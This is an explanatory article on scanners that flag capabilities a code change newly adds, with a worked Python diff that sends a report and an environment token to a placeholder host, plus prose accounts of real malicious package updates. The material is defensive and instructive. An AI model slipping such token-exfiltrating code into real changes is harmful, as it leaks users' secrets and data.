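# Detecting Newly Introduced Capabilities in a Code Change: Network, Subprocess, File and Secret Access

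## What does it mean for a code change to add a capability?

A program's capabilities are the kinds of access it has outside itself, such as sending data over a network, starting other programs, writing files or reading stored passwords. A code change can add a capability. Tools that detect such additions mostly grew out of efforts to stop attackers from slipping hostile code into widely shared software libraries. Using them routinely in code review is still a new idea. At an industry meeting on supply-chain security in September 2025, participants discussed "capability-change diffs" as a new signal for reviewers. According to *S3C2 Summit 2025-09* (2026), an account of that meeting, these diffs are meant to direct attention to what a change newly allows the software to do, rather than how the code looks.

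### Diffs, pull requests and package updates

A diff lists the lines added and removed between two versions of a program. In the common "unified" format, which GNU documents, added lines begin with a plus sign, removed lines with a minus sign, and unchanged lines with a space.

On a team, a diff usually arrives in a pull request. GitHub's *About pull requests* defines a pull request as a proposal to merge code changes from one branch (a separate line of work on the same code) into another. Colleagues comment on the changed lines and automated checks run against them before anyone merges the change.

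A package is a reusable library that its maintainers publish on a registry, such as npm for JavaScript or PyPI for Python. A package update is a new published version. Programs that depend on the package may install the update automatically, and their owners rarely read the diff.

A small example shows most of the difficulties. A company has a report exporter, a Python program. Somebody files an issue, which is a written request in the project's tracker: the exporter prints 03/04/2026, half the readers take that for the third of April, and it should print 2026-03-04. This patch comes back:

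```diff
+import os
+from http.client import HTTPSConnection
+
 def export_report(report):
-    day = report.date.strftime("%m/%d/%Y")
+    day = report.date.strftime("%Y-%m-%d")
     text = render(report, day)
+    token = os.environ["REPORTS_TOKEN"]
+    server = HTTPSConnection("collector.example")
+    server.request("POST", "/reports", text, {"Authorization": token})
     return text
```

The line that replaces the removed one fixes the date. The last three added lines read an API token from the program's environment, the named settings it receives when it starts. The token is a password-like string that identifies the program to an online service. The lines then send the report, with the token attached, to a machine called collector.example. None of this is in the issue, but many legitimate programs upload their reports this way.

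### Which kinds of access count

Most tools work from a list. Rahman, Paramitha and colleagues (2024), in *What's in a Package?*, built one for Java: 227 library functions that can reach the filesystem, the network or system processes, sorted into 15 capabilities. Google, whose Capslock tool reports capabilities for the Go language, describes them as the privileged operations that the code accesses. (The Linux kernel has an unrelated use for the word. In the Linux manual's *capabilities(7)*, capabilities are the units into which the kernel divides an administrator's privileges.)

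The kinds that come up most often look like this in code, in Python except for the last:

| Capability | One-line example | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| Outbound network | `urlopen(address, data=report)` | Sends the report to a web address |
| Process execution | `subprocess.run(["git", "pull"])` | Starts another program, here git |
| File write | `open("report.csv", "w").write(text)` | Creates or overwrites a file |
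| Environment read | `os.environ["REPORTS_TOKEN"]` | Fetches a setting, often a secret |
| Credential read | `open("/home/ana/.aws/credentials").read()` | Reads stored login keys for a cloud service |
| Install script | `"postinstall": "node setup.js"` | Runs `setup.js` when someone installs the package |

These kinds of access are not equally powerful. Deno, a program for running JavaScript, denies all such access by default and makes the user grant each kind separately. But Deno's *Security and permissions* warns that permission to start other programs is effectively permission to do everything. The new program runs outside Deno's restrictions, so a script without network access can start a program that has it.

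Install scripts differ from the other entries in the table because they determine when code runs more than what it can reach. Datadog's *Introducing GuardDog 3.0* (2026), which describes a free scanner for malicious packages, lists them as an "execution vector", separate from the credential theft that may follow. They still belong in the table because a package that gains an install script can act on a machine before anyone has used the package. Deno's *Permissions* gives the risk of arbitrary code execution as the reason Deno leaves npm's post-install scripts switched off.

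Every list also includes some debatable classifications. Rahman and colleagues count a call to Java's standard logging function as file output, which is technically correct but usually uninteresting. They put encryption and encoding under "process" after their two raters agreed that neither of the other two headings fitted. These decisions affect how often a scanner that uses the list raises an alarm.

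### The definition as a difference between two sets

Write C(v) for the set of capabilities that version v of the code has. Then a change adds

C(after) − C(before),

that is, everything in the later set that is missing from the earlier one. If the old exporter only turned a report into text, C(before) is empty and C(after) contains outbound network and environment read. Those two are the new capabilities. The date fix contributes nothing to either set.

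A search for suspicious words in the added lines can flag a change that adds no capability under this definition. If a programmer moves an existing upload function to another file, the diff shows a network call on an added line, but the program could already make that call.

Jandali, Sheybani and colleagues (2026), in *Preflight*, use the same subtraction for updates to Python packages. They run the old and new versions through the functions that a particular application uses, record what each version does, and subtract one record from the other. They compare versions because harmless software also opens connections, writes files and starts programs all the time, so such behavior is stronger evidence of harm when an update introduces it than when it was already there.

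The result then depends on the baseline, the recorded set that stands in for C(before). Jandali and colleagues point out that an earlier version is a reference for behavior, not proof of harmlessness. If it already contained the attacker's code, the subtraction hides that code. When there is no usable earlier version, their tool compares against an empty set, so everything it observes remains after the subtraction. In one such case, two of the three network addresses behind a "malicious" verdict belonged to the testing environment. The researchers therefore use "newly introduced" only for comparisons with a real earlier version.

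We can only estimate C(v). Static analysis examines the code without running it. Dynamic analysis, also called behavioral analysis, runs the code in a monitored environment and records what happens. *Evolution of Android's Permission-based Security Model and Challenges* (2026) notes that static analysis can cover all the paths through a program but yields only hypothetical behavior, while dynamic analysis yields real behavior but only on the paths that the tests reach.

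A test can easily miss the exporter's upload. If nobody has set `REPORTS_TOKEN` on the test machine, the program stops with an error at the line that reads it, before the upload, and the recording shows no network use. A static scanner would find the upload quickly, but it could not determine whether anyone ever calls `export_report`. An error in the estimate for either version carries over into the difference between them. For example, a tool that misses a network call in the old version but detects it in the new one will report a capability that is not new.

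### New at what level of detail?

So far the old exporter had no outside access at all, which makes the answer easy. Suppose instead that it already downloaded exchange rates from rates.example with Python's `urlopen` function, and read its display language from the environment. The same patch now gives different answers at different levels:

| Level of detail | Already present | Added by the patch |
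|---|---|---|
| Kind of access | Network, environment read | Nothing |
| Library function | `urlopen`, `os.environ` | `HTTPSConnection.request` |
| Destination or variable | rates.example, `REPORT_LANG` | collector.example, `REPORTS_TOKEN` |

The patch sends company reports to a new place, but at the coarsest level of detail it adds no capability. We therefore have to choose a level before we can say whether a change adds a capability.

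Researchers define capabilities at different levels of detail. Rahman and colleagues report four levels: three broad resources, 15 capabilities, 227 functions, and the number of calls to those functions. One Java package in their study, guice, calls the logging function 35 times, which counts as 35 calls but only one function and one capability. Ohm, Pohl and Boes (2023), in *You Can Run But You Can't Hide*, use two levels for JavaScript. Their coarse set records which built-in modules and global objects a package uses, and their fine set adds the individual operations within them. The difference matters for a module like `fs`, which groups all file operations together. If a package already uses `fs` to read a settings file, an update that starts writing files adds a new operation to the fine set but leaves the coarse set unchanged.

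Deno lets a user allow all network access or only one named host, and all environment variables or only one. Preflight similarly distinguishes between destinations by comparing the addresses that a package contacts.

Library function and destination are two separate scales, and a finer comparison is not necessarily better. If a programmer swaps `urlopen` for another networking library and still contacts only rates.example, comparing by function shows a difference that comparing by destination does not. Finer comparisons also produce more differences for people to read, most of them harmless ones like this.

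Whether a change adds a capability depends as much on how much code is compared as on how finely capabilities are defined. Ohm and colleagues define a package's capabilities as the union of the capabilities of its files. If one file has always used the network, a second file can start using it without changing the union. Some part of a large application nearly always has network access, so a coarse comparison of the whole program will almost never find a new network capability, whereas a comparison of `export_report` alone would find one.

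### New, malicious, or unrequested

After a scanner flags the exporter patch, a reviewer may want to know whether the capability is new, whether the change is malicious, and whether anybody requested the addition. The subtraction can't answer all three questions, and each needs separate evidence.

Novelty needs two versions of the code and a level of detail. With the original exporter, the answer is yes.

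Malice depends on facts that the diff does not contain. The example patch is at worst careless if collector.example is the company's own archive, but it steals both reports and a token if a stranger runs the site. In *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs*, Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues describe a closely similar real commit to the software project Nx, which took a publishing token from the environment and sent it to an outside web address. They argue that conventional static tools mainly catch known bad patterns and do not assess intent, so they can fail to distinguish a legitimate change from abuse. Datadog builds the same distinction into GuardDog, which combines one set of rules for capabilities, "not necessarily malicious", with another for signs of a threat, such as suspicious domain names.

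Whether anybody requested the upload depends on the task scope, which is what the request permits, explicitly or by implication. A request to correct a date format plausibly covers a new test for the format and an edit to the manual, but it is hard to read it as covering an upload. If the issue had also included "and send each report to the archive", the same three lines would have been part of the requested work.

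Whether a capability is new, whether anyone requested it and whether it is harmful are separate questions, and most combinations of answers are possible. An overhelpful colleague may add an upload that is new, unrequested and harmless. An attacker who takes over a program that already uploads reports can redirect them without adding a capability, if "any network use" counts as a single capability.

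Different groups look for different things in a code change. People who monitor package registries look for new behavior and treat it as a possible sign of malice. The Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF) runs *Package Analysis*, a project that records which files packages access, which addresses they contact and which commands they run, and tracks changes over time to detect when safe software becomes suspicious. Company security teams mainly want to know whether a change is malicious. At Datadog, where Lamb and colleagues work, a language model classifies pull requests as benign or malicious. People who direct or train AI coding agents also worry that an agent with no hostile aim may do more than its user authorized. *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits* (Lim and Neo, 2026) calls this tendency overeagerness.

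### How to score a scanner

Google's guide for developers gives the standard formulas for three measures of how well a scanner does. In an invented example, a scanner checks 1,000 changes, of which 10 are malicious. It flags 50, and 8 of those are malicious.

- Recall is the share of the items looked for that the scanner flags: 8 of 10, or 80 percent.
- The false positive rate is the share of harmless items that it flags: 42 of 990, or about 4 percent.
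- Precision is the share of flagged items that are what the scanner is looking for: 8 of 50, or 16 percent.

Even with a false positive rate of 4 percent, more than four in five of these alarms are false, because malicious changes are so rare that a small share of the harmless ones outnumbers them.

The precision of the same 50 flags also depends on what counts as a correct flag. Suppose 45 of the flagged changes add a capability, 20 add one nobody requested, and 8 are malicious. The scanner's precision is then 90 percent for new capabilities, 40 percent for unrequested ones and 16 percent for malice. Readers can learn little from a published precision figure unless they know which of these counted as a correct flag.

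Precision usually falls as recall rises. Datadog observes that a tool that flags every package finds all the malicious ones but has low precision. Plain accuracy, the share of all verdicts that are right, is misleading for events this rare, because a scanner that never flagged anything would be correct on about 99 percent of these 1,000 changes.

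## How does a scanner find new calls by comparing code before and after a change?

A scanner first lists the capabilities of the code before and after the change by searching each version for calls that someone has already linked to a capability. Each match is a finding, which consists of the rule that matched, the location in a file and usually a short message. The scanner then pairs the findings that occur in both versions and reports any unpaired findings from the new version.

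For the report exporter the steps look like this:

1. The scanner reads the file as it stood before the patch and as it stands after it.
2. It works out where each name comes from. `HTTPSConnection` belongs to Python's `http.client` module, and `os` is the operating-system module.
3. It looks the names up in a table, in which `http.client.HTTPSConnection` means outbound network and `os.environ` means environment read.
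4. The old version yields no findings. The new version yields two, one on the `token` line and one on the `server` line.
5. Neither has a partner in the old version, so the scanner reports both as new.

People write the table in step 3 by hand, and it can be short. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*, compared 11 tools for JavaScript packages. One of them, Packj, maps 56 JavaScript functions to 10 permission categories and flags any package that calls one of the 56. Gobbi and Kinder (2024), in *GENIE*, give examples of calls that often turn up in malicious packages, under four headings:

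| Heading | Example calls |
|---|---|
| Network | `http.get`, `request.write`, `dns.resolve` |
| File system | `fs.readFile`, `fs.writeFile`, `os.homedir` |
| Process | `child_process.exec`, `process.env` |
| Code generation | `eval`, `vm.runInContext` |

The last heading covers functions that run text as code. The "process" heading includes both a call that starts programs and `process.env`, which reads environment variables. Gobbi and Kinder use the headings to describe attacks, and this grouping does no harm there. But if a package already started programs, a tool that compared versions by heading would miss an update that begins to read secrets from the environment.

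### Text rules and syntax-tree rules

A text rule looks for a pattern of characters. It is quick to write and runs on almost any file, but it can match in the wrong place and miss the right one. Take a rule that searches for `HTTPSConnection(` in this code:

```python
# TODO: stop using HTTPSConnection(host) here
from http.client import HTTPSConnection as Connection
server = Connection("collector.example")
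```

A rule that searches for text can match a mention of a call in a comment and miss an actual call in the code. Guo and colleagues found false matches of the first kind in OSSGadget, a Microsoft scanner whose rules match `curl` and `wget`, the names of two download programs, in README files and comments. They think changing the rules can't fully fix the problem. Chainguard's *malcontent* (2025), which documents a scanner with more than 14,500 rules, warns that other malware scanners may report malcontent as malicious because its rules contain the strings those scanners look for.

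A syntax-tree rule checks the tree that a parser builds from source code, which contains elements such as imports, calls and strings. The tree lets the scanner distinguish calls from comments and trace `Connection` back to `http.client`. In Semgrep, a widely used scanner, such rules can be written as code fragments with blanks. For example, the pattern `sink($X)` matches a call to `sink` with any single argument.

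CodeQL, GitHub's analysis engine, stores the tree in a database that people search with queries. The database also records the order in which statements can run and the paths that values can take through the program. Gobbi and Kinder give a very short query that finds the web requests in a JavaScript program, whichever request library the program uses, provided CodeQL has a description of that library. They point out that with Semgrep they would have had to write a new pattern for each library. Their CodeQL queries also work on code with shortened variable names and no unnecessary spaces, which is common in published JavaScript packages.

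Syntax-tree rules need a parser for every language and source code to parse. Malcontent also inspects compiled programs and container images (packaged copies of a program with everything it needs to run), so it relies on text and byte patterns. For source code that parses, a syntax-tree match is better evidence that a call exists than a pattern match.

### Searching the added lines or both whole versions

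The simplest comparison runs the rules only on the added lines, which a diff marks with a plus sign. This works for the exporter patch because the patch adds both the imports and the calls. If the file had already imported `HTTPSConnection` under another name, the added lines alone would not show what that name referred to.

GitHub avoids this problem by analyzing the whole program and reporting only the alerts that involve changed lines. As *Using incremental analysis with the CodeQL CLI* explains, the user converts the diff into line ranges in the new file and keeps an alert if its main location or a related location falls within one. In the document's example, two inserted lines become the range 16 to 17 and one modified line becomes 27 to 27. A deletion produces no range. To save time, CodeQL can also reuse a stored database of the main branch and process only the changed files.

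Until March 2023, GitHub showed every code scanning alert unique to a pull request's branch, including alerts unrelated to the change, according to its *Code scanning shows more accurate and relevant alerts on pull requests* (2023). Since then, it has shown only alerts inside the changed lines, and reviewers have to open a separate page to see the rest. This suits a reviewer who has to fix the alerts, but it works poorly for finding new capabilities, because a change on one line can alter what another line does.

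Suppose a file imports a function called `run`, which does nothing, from the team's own test code and calls it forty lines further down. A patch changes only the import, so that `run` now comes from Python's `subprocess` module. The unchanged call now starts another program. Scanning both full versions of the file finds a process call only in the new one. A filter that keeps only findings on changed lines would drop this one, unless the rule also lists the import as a related location.

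When Semgrep scans a pull request, it first scans the files at the tip of the new branch, then goes back to the commit where the branch started and checks which findings were already there. In an example from its documentation, the first scan covers 52 files and produces 60 findings, while the second covers only 4 files because it needs only the files and rules that produced a finding the first time. If all the findings are in newly created files, Semgrep skips the second scan, since nothing in those files can have existed before. GitLab, a code-hosting service, says its own analyzer scans the modified files and a limited neighborhood of files around them.

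Some changes escape both methods. For example, a program might upload reports only after checking that the user agreed, and a patch might delete that check. The program can now upload reports without the user's agreement, but the diff contains no added line, and a comparison of calls correctly finds no new call because the upload call is in both versions.

### Recognizing an old finding in a new place

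The scanner searches both versions of the code, then has to match the findings that appear in both. Line numbers are unreliable for matching because inserting one line changes the number of every line below it.

Li and Yang (2022), in *Tracking the Evolution of Static Code Warnings*, measured how often this step goes wrong. They applied an established matching method to warnings from two bug finders, SpotBugs and PMD, in four large Java projects. The method makes up to four attempts to match each warning, looking first for a warning with identical details, then for one at most three lines away after adjusting for the diff, then for an identical piece of code, and finally for similar surrounding text. Any warning in the new version that remains unmatched counts as newly introduced.

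Of the 1,445 warnings that the method reported as new, 999 (69.1 percent) were new. The other 446 already existed. In one of the paper's examples, three similar warnings are on lines 201, 203 and 205, and a commit moves them to lines 205, 207 and 209 without altering them. The method looks for exact matches first, so it pairs the old warning on line 205 with the one now on line 205, which was originally on line 201. It then wrongly reports the warnings on lines 207 and 209 as new.

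Li and Yang examined 1,174 mistakes, including warnings wrongly labeled as removed. Shifted code of this kind accounted for 366 of them, and renaming and other restructuring accounted for 437. Their method recognizes common restructurings and looks for the best overall pairing of warnings, while the old method took the first acceptable match for each one. Their method raised precision on removed and new warnings combined from 64.4 to 90.3 percent.

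These are warnings about bugs in Java, and the rate for capability findings may differ. The sample also includes only warnings that the old method had classified as removed or new, so it leaves out the majority, which are easy to match. In one commit, 3,137 of 3,163 pairings were exact matches. But the errors are concentrated in the list of supposedly new findings, which is the only list a reviewer reads.

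Semgrep computes a fingerprint from the file path, the rule's name and the rule's pattern with its blanks filled in from the code, but not from the line number. For example, a rule might look for `spcd.get($X)` followed later by `sink($X)`, and match a file where both calls have the argument `"foo"`. Inserting an unrelated line between the two calls doesn't change the filled-in pattern, so the fingerprint stays the same. After computing the fingerprint, Semgrep appends a counter so that a second identical match in the same file gets its own fingerprint.

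Because the fingerprint includes the file path, an upload function moved to another file gets a new fingerprint and looks new. Comparing the whole program's set of capabilities before and after the change avoids this but misses a second, unrelated upload if the program already had one. The matching key therefore determines, often implicitly, the level of detail at which a capability counts as new.

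### Forty-one queries on npm updates

Froh, Gobbi and Kinder (2023), in *Differential Static Analysis for Detecting Malicious Updates to Open Source Packages*, took the method all the way from rules to results. They wrote 41 CodeQL queries for JavaScript packages on npm (the description of their tests mentions 40), in six classes:

| Class | What the queries look for |
|---|---|
| Network | Web requests, and data that flows into them |
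| Process | Operating-system commands and newly started programs |
| File access | Operations on system or user files, and the data involved |
| Obfuscation | Code that someone has transformed to conceal what it does |
| Metadata | New dependencies and suspicious installation scripts |
| Code generation | Functions such as `eval` that run text as code |

The list includes both capabilities and other warning signs. Obfuscation, for example, doesn't give a program access to anything, but attackers can use it to hide what their code does.

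For each update, the tool downloads two consecutive versions, builds a database for each, runs all the queries on both and compares the results. It treats two findings as the same if they have the same alert message and file path, regardless of line number. The message must contain the relevant code, so if an update changes that code, the finding counts as new.

Their worked example is conventional-changelog, a package for generating release notes. In version 1.1.24 its main file loads two modules, prepares some options and hands them on, and nothing in it is suspicious. In version 1.2.0 an attacker had added a few lines. They import Node's function for starting programs, store a long encoded string, decode it and run the result as a shell script whenever somebody uses the package. The script started a cryptocurrency miner. The comparison leaves five new findings:

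1. The file imports `child_process`, the module for starting programs.
2. It starts a new process as a shell script.
3. It decodes a string from Base64, a common way of writing data as plain letters and digits.
4. The encoded string flows into the argument of the new process.
5. The encoded string passes through the decoding step and then into that argument.

A reviewer could tell roughly what had happened from the fifth finding alone. If version 1.1.24 had already imported `child_process` in the same file, the scanner would not have reported the first finding but would still have reported the others.

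Every query has a severity from 0 to 10, which Froh and colleagues set based on their knowledge of malware and how often the pattern occurs in it. The tool adds up the severities of the queries with new findings, counting each query only once, and flags the update if the total reaches 10. A single finding of severity 10 is enough. As an invented example, the tool flags an update with new findings for queries of severity 2, 4 and 7, because the total is 13. An update with ten new matches for only the severity 4 query scores 4 and passes.

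The first test used nine packages, each with one known malicious version. The tool flagged all nine malicious updates. It also flagged four harmless updates, three of pm-controls and one of ua-parser-js.

The second test covered 6,361 versions of 25 popular packages, and the tool flagged 89 of them, or 1.4 percent. (The rows of the results table add up to 82 of 6,117, which gives almost the same rate.) The web framework vue had 36 flagged versions, or 8.1 percent of its versions, and the build tool webpack had 14, while 13 of the 25 packages had none. Froh and colleagues counted every flag as a false alarm without checking it, because nobody had publicly reported a malicious version of these packages. That is a reasonable way to judge malice, but it doesn't show how many of the flagged versions had gained a capability, so the 1.4 percent is not an error rate for detecting new capabilities.

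The nine out of nine result deserves less weight than the 1.4 percent figure. The queries were based partly on two malware collections that contain some of the malicious versions tested. Froh and colleagues acknowledge this overlap but expect its effect to be small, because the queries describe general behavior and not particular packages. Nine cases is also a small sample. Even without any overlap, a tool that catches only three quarters of malicious updates would catch all nine about one time in thirteen.

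The design has two further limits. The tool can only find behavior that one of its queries describes, so detecting a new kind of attack requires a new query. It also doesn't count a finding as new if the same message already occurs in that file. For example, if a program already runs a command in one function and an update runs the same command in another function of the same file, the tool doesn't report the addition. Semgrep's counter addresses this case, but it probably can't always tell which of two identical matches is new, since the count depends on their order in the file.

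Froh and colleagues note that the two versions could also be two commits in a project, though they tested only published packages.

### GuardDog's move from Semgrep to YARA

GuardDog, Datadog's free scanner, has moved the opposite way, from structured rules to text patterns. Datadog's *Finding malicious PyPI packages through static code analysis* (2022) describes the original design, which used Semgrep rules. Some of these rules followed data from one call to another. A simplified example looks for code that reads the machine's name, or one of two environment variables that hold Amazon cloud keys, and sends the value out with the Python library `requests`.

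That rule would be right nearly every time it fired on a secret key, but it would miss the exporter patch for two reasons. `REPORTS_TOKEN` is not one of the two variables, and `HTTPSConnection` is not part of `requests`.

Datadog said it dropped Semgrep in GuardDog 3.0, released in June 2026, partly because its Semgrep rules fitted known examples of malware too closely and made new malware harder to identify. Semgrep also used a lot of memory on large files and was slow on packages with many files, partly because it starts a new process for every scan. GuardDog now uses YARA, a language for text and byte patterns that is popular with malware analysts, through a library that runs inside GuardDog's own process.

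Guo and colleagues ran the older version on packages averaging 47 files and found it the fastest of the tools they timed, at 2.55 seconds per package. They and Datadog may both be right about its speed, since Datadog's complaint was about large files and large packages. The researchers also rated the old version the best balanced of the conventional detectors. Two of its 22 rules, one for install scripts and one for suspicious links, produced more than 90 percent of its detections, which suggests that many of the narrower rules seldom mattered.

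Broad text patterns produce many more matches, so GuardDog 3.0 needs a way to rank them. Version 2.0 listed every match, while the new version checks where its capability rules and threat rules both match. Besides suspicious domains, the threat rules cover indicators such as sensitive file names and routines that unscramble hidden code. According to Datadog's *GuardDog*, the scanner's documentation, a capability and a threat indicator in the same file form a risk. They also form a risk if they are in different files, but at a lower severity.

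Each kind of match is weak evidence alone. A networking library ought to make network requests, and a suspicious domain name may come from a test. DefectDojo, which collects results from many scanners, applies the same logic when it imports GuardDog's output. It rates a capability match that is not part of a risk as informational, and a lone threat match as medium severity.

A capability rule for outbound connections could match the exporter's new `HTTPSConnection` line. If no threat rule covers a variable name like `REPORTS_TOKEN` or an address like collector.example, the scanner classifies the upload only as a capability.

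GuardDog combines the risks into a score from 0 to 10, using four factors:

| Factor | Weight | What it measures |
|---|---|---|
| Maximal severity | 30% | The most severe risk in the package |
| Completeness of the attack chain | 20% | Whether the risks cover several stages of an attack, from getting in to sending data out |
| Specificity | 30% | How typical the matched code is of malware, as opposed to ordinary software |
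| Sophistication | 20% | How advanced the techniques are |

Datadog set both the weights and the labels by its own judgment. In June 2026 a score of 4 meant "low risk, likely benign", but by August the documentation for version 3.2.0 rated scores from 3.1 to 7.5 as medium risk. Recording the version along with the score would help anyone who automatically blocks "medium" packages know which ratings applied.

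The move also removes the old Semgrep rule's requirement that the secret reach the request. Two YARA matches in one file show only that both are present, and a large file may well contain a harmless request and an unrelated mention of a password file.

GuardDog scores one version of a package at a time, apart from a rule that checks newly added dependencies, so a high score doesn't mean that the latest update caused it. Malcontent, which also uses YARA rules, has a diff mode that compares a release with the previous one. It marks each added capability with two plus signs and a risk score based on how specific that capability is to malware. Chainguard adds that the version number indicates how large a change to expect. A jump from 1.0.1 to 1.0.2 normally means a small fix, so a new network connection would be out of place. By default, malcontent also raises a file's risk when matches become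 more frequent, whereas Froh and colleagues' scoring ignores repeats.

Thomas Strömberg, who works on malcontent at Chainguard, describes a comparison in which one file's risk rose from medium to critical between two revisions. He doesn't expect any tool to be fully reliable at deciding whether code is malicious. The comparison shows the new behaviors to a reviewer who knows what the library is for, and who then judges whether they are reasonable.

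### Calls that the rules cannot see

All these rules depend on finding a recognizable call in the code. Some programs choose at runtime which module to load or which function to call, often for innocent reasons such as supporting plug-ins. The source code then contains no fixed name for a rule to match, so a scanner can report at most that something gets loaded.

Obfuscation has the same effect on purpose. Gobbi and Kinder found that the stronger transformations, including the default settings of a popular JavaScript tool, prevent CodeQL from following data through the program. They argue that scanners should treat obfuscated code as suspicious in itself, and wrote queries to detect it. Comparing versions suits this approach well because even if the scanner can't read the obfuscated code, it can report that a previously readable package now contains some.

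Guo and colleagues checked 6,420 malicious npm package versions for eight kinds of evasion and found none in 80.3 percent of them. The sample included only malware that had already been caught, so well-hidden code is probably underrepresented. The researchers attribute the high percentage to npm not requiring a scan before a package is published. If they are right, more malware should use evasion once registries begin to scan, and simple rules would then catch less of it than they do now.

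## What if the new call is reached through another function or package?

Suppose the company already has a helper function called `notify`, in a separate file, which posts messages to its chat service. Whoever fixes the exporter's date format also adds a call to it:

```diff
+from alerts import notify
+
 def export_report(report):
-    day = report.date.strftime("%m/%d/%Y")
+    day = report.date.strftime("%Y-%m-%d")
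     text = render(report, day)
+    notify("Report exported", text)
     return text
```

No added line names a network function. The request is in `alerts.py`, which the patch doesn't touch:

```python
def notify(title, body):
    post_message(title + "\n" + body)

def post_message(message):
    urlopen("https://chat.example/hook", data=message.encode())
```

`export_report` used to only return text, and now it also sends that text to a chat service. Rules that search the added lines miss this change. Scanning both whole versions misses it too, because the `urlopen` call is in both, so the scanner pairs the two findings and reports nothing new.

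A call graph exposes the change. It is a map of the program with an arrow from each function to every function it can call. Leaving out the date formatting, the arrows that start at `export_report` are:

```text
Before:  export_report → render

After:   export_report → render
         export_report → notify → post_message → urlopen (network)
```

A tool that follows the calls reaches `urlopen` only in the new version, so network access is new for `export_report`. Whether it is new for the whole program depends on whether other code already called `notify`. If it did, the program could already post to the chat service. If not, the patch has made unused code reachable, and the whole program has gained network access too.

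### How Capslock follows the calls

Google's Capslock does this for programs written in Go. When Google announced the tool in 2023, it argued that a package should have only the access its job requires, and that nobody would expect a logging library to be able to run remote code. Google's *capslock* (2025) describes the method as following "transitive calls", which are calls that pass through other functions. The steps are:

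1. Capslock loads the chosen packages and everything they depend on.
2. It builds the call graph.
3. It marks the sensitive functions in Go's standard library, using a table that people maintain. The table first assigns a capability to a whole package and then makes exceptions for single functions. Everything in the `os` package starts out as OPERATING_SYSTEM, for example, but `os.Chown`, which changes a file's owner, counts as FILES.
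4. It searches the graph for paths from the chosen packages to the marked functions.
5. It reports each capability it finds, and can print an example of a call path that leads to it.

The table can also mark a function as safe, which ends the search there. According to Google, the result has one entry for each combination of function and capability by default, but it can instead have one per package. Either way, the user gets an example path, not every path, so removing the reported call may not remove the capability.

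Google's *Examples* applies Capslock to code from an attempted attack in August 2022, in which somebody copied thousands of GitHub projects and added a short function to them. The function was named `init`, so Go would run it automatically when the program started. It sent all the environment variables to a web address and ran whatever came back as a shell command. Capslock reported eight capabilities for it, including NETWORK, EXEC and READ_SYSTEM_STATE. It also reported FILES, although no line of the function explicitly opens a file.

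Harmless programs produce long lists too. Capslock's analysis of itself finds seven capabilities, including EXEC. The example path for EXEC runs through six functions, from Capslock's main function through Go's package-loading library to the standard function for starting a program. This is harmless because Capslock has to load packages, but a reviewer has to read the path to know that. Even Google's explanation of a second, longer path seems to contain a mistake. It attributes the OPERATING_SYSTEM capability to the protobuf library, but after Capslock's own code, the path goes only through Go's tools library until it reaches the standard library.

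Large libraries have more of these paths than anyone will read. For a 2023 development version of gRPC, a library that lets programs call each other over a network, deps.dev's *google.golang.org/grpc* page lists 9 direct and 871 indirect entries for starting other programs.

### What Capslock reports, and where it has to stop

Google defines the following capabilities, leaving aside two labels that only steer the search:

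| Capability | What it covers |
|---|---|
| FILES | Reading or changing files, directories and file permissions |
| NETWORK | Connecting to other machines, or listening for connections |
| EXEC | Starting other programs |
| READ_SYSTEM_STATE | Reading environment variables, network interfaces or process details |
| MODIFY_SYSTEM_STATE | Setting environment variables or changing the working directory |
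| OPERATING_SYSTEM | Anything else in Go's `os` package |
| SYSTEM_CALLS | Direct requests to the operating system's kernel |
| RUNTIME | Sensitive parts of Go's own machinery, such as memory clean-up |
| CGO | Calls into C code |
| UNSAFE_POINTER | Raw memory pointers, which bypass Go's type checks |
| ARBITRARY_EXECUTION | Assembly code and other operations that can do anything |
| REFLECT | Reflection, which lets a program inspect values and call functions chosen at runtime |
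| UNANALYZED | Call paths that Capslock could not follow |

The list is coarse in places that matter for code review. FILES covers both reading and writing, while *GoLeash* (2025), which watches Go programs as they run, separates the two. READ_SYSTEM_STATE covers reading both a secret token and the name of the current directory. The names may still change before version 1.0, and MacPorts' *capslock* showed version 0.3.2 in August 2026.

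The last five rows describe code whose behavior Capslock can't determine. Google's *Caveats* says that if the analysis can't establish that a use of reflection is harmless, Capslock reports the reflection itself, so that users at least learn of the gap. It does the same for C code, assembly and unsafe pointers. It also reports code that starts another program, because it can't determine what that program will do. However, Capslock doesn't warn about code that might let two parts of a Go program change the same variable at the same time, which can cause arbitrary behavior for some types of variable.

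Reporting the gap works well for a first look at a package but less well for comparing versions. If a package already has the REFLECT capability, an update can use reflection to reach the network without adding anything to the package's list of capabilities.

The results also differ by operating system. Go projects can include files that are compiled only on Windows or only on Linux, and Capslock reads only the files that a build for the selected system would use. An upload in a Windows-only file won't appear in an analysis for Linux. Users can select the system with a setting, but a project that ships for three systems needs three analyses.

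### Comparing revisions and committing a baseline

Google's *capslock-git-diff* (2025) lists the package capabilities added between two revisions of a project. The command `capslock-git-diff main mybranch` compares a proposed branch with the main one, and replacing `mybranch` with `.` compares the main branch with the current code on the programmer's machine.

Capslock can also compare a later run against the results of an earlier version, which the user saves and passes in as a file (Google, *Using Capslock*). The command exits with status code 1 if it finds a difference (Google, *capslock*, 2024), so an automated build can stop.

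git-pkgs' *capcheck* (2026) turns this into a routine. A project runs capcheck once and commits the resulting list of capabilities, the lock file, alongside its code. From then on the automated checks on each pull request repeat the analysis and fail if the list has grown. The error message includes the path. In the documentation's example, a web server gains EXEC because its upload handler calls an image-resizing library, which starts another program. The programmer either removes the call or runs an update command and commits the longer list.

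That second option puts the new capability into the diff as a changed line, which a reviewer can question. But the person who wrote the change can also run the update command, so the check works only if somebody reads changes to the lock file.

Would capcheck catch the call to `notify` in a Go version of the exporter? That depends on two settings, the level of detail and the list of capabilities to ignore:

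- By default, it compares whole packages. If `export_report` and `notify` are in the same package, that package already had network access and the check passes. If they are in different packages, the exporter's package gains NETWORK and the check fails. Comparing by function catches both cases, but git-pkgs warns that the lock file then becomes much larger and changes more often.
- The sample configuration ignores FILES, NETWORK, REFLECT and RUNTIME because they are noisy. With those settings the check passes whatever the level of detail.

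git-pkgs recommends that most projects watch only for EXEC, CGO, ARBITRARY_EXECUTION, UNSAFE_POINTER and MODIFY_SYSTEM_STATE. This is sensible advice for a team that wants few alarms about its dependencies, but it removes the two capabilities that a team worried about leaking reports would care about most. The lock file also has to come from the same operating system setting every time, because a list made for macOS won't match one made for Linux.

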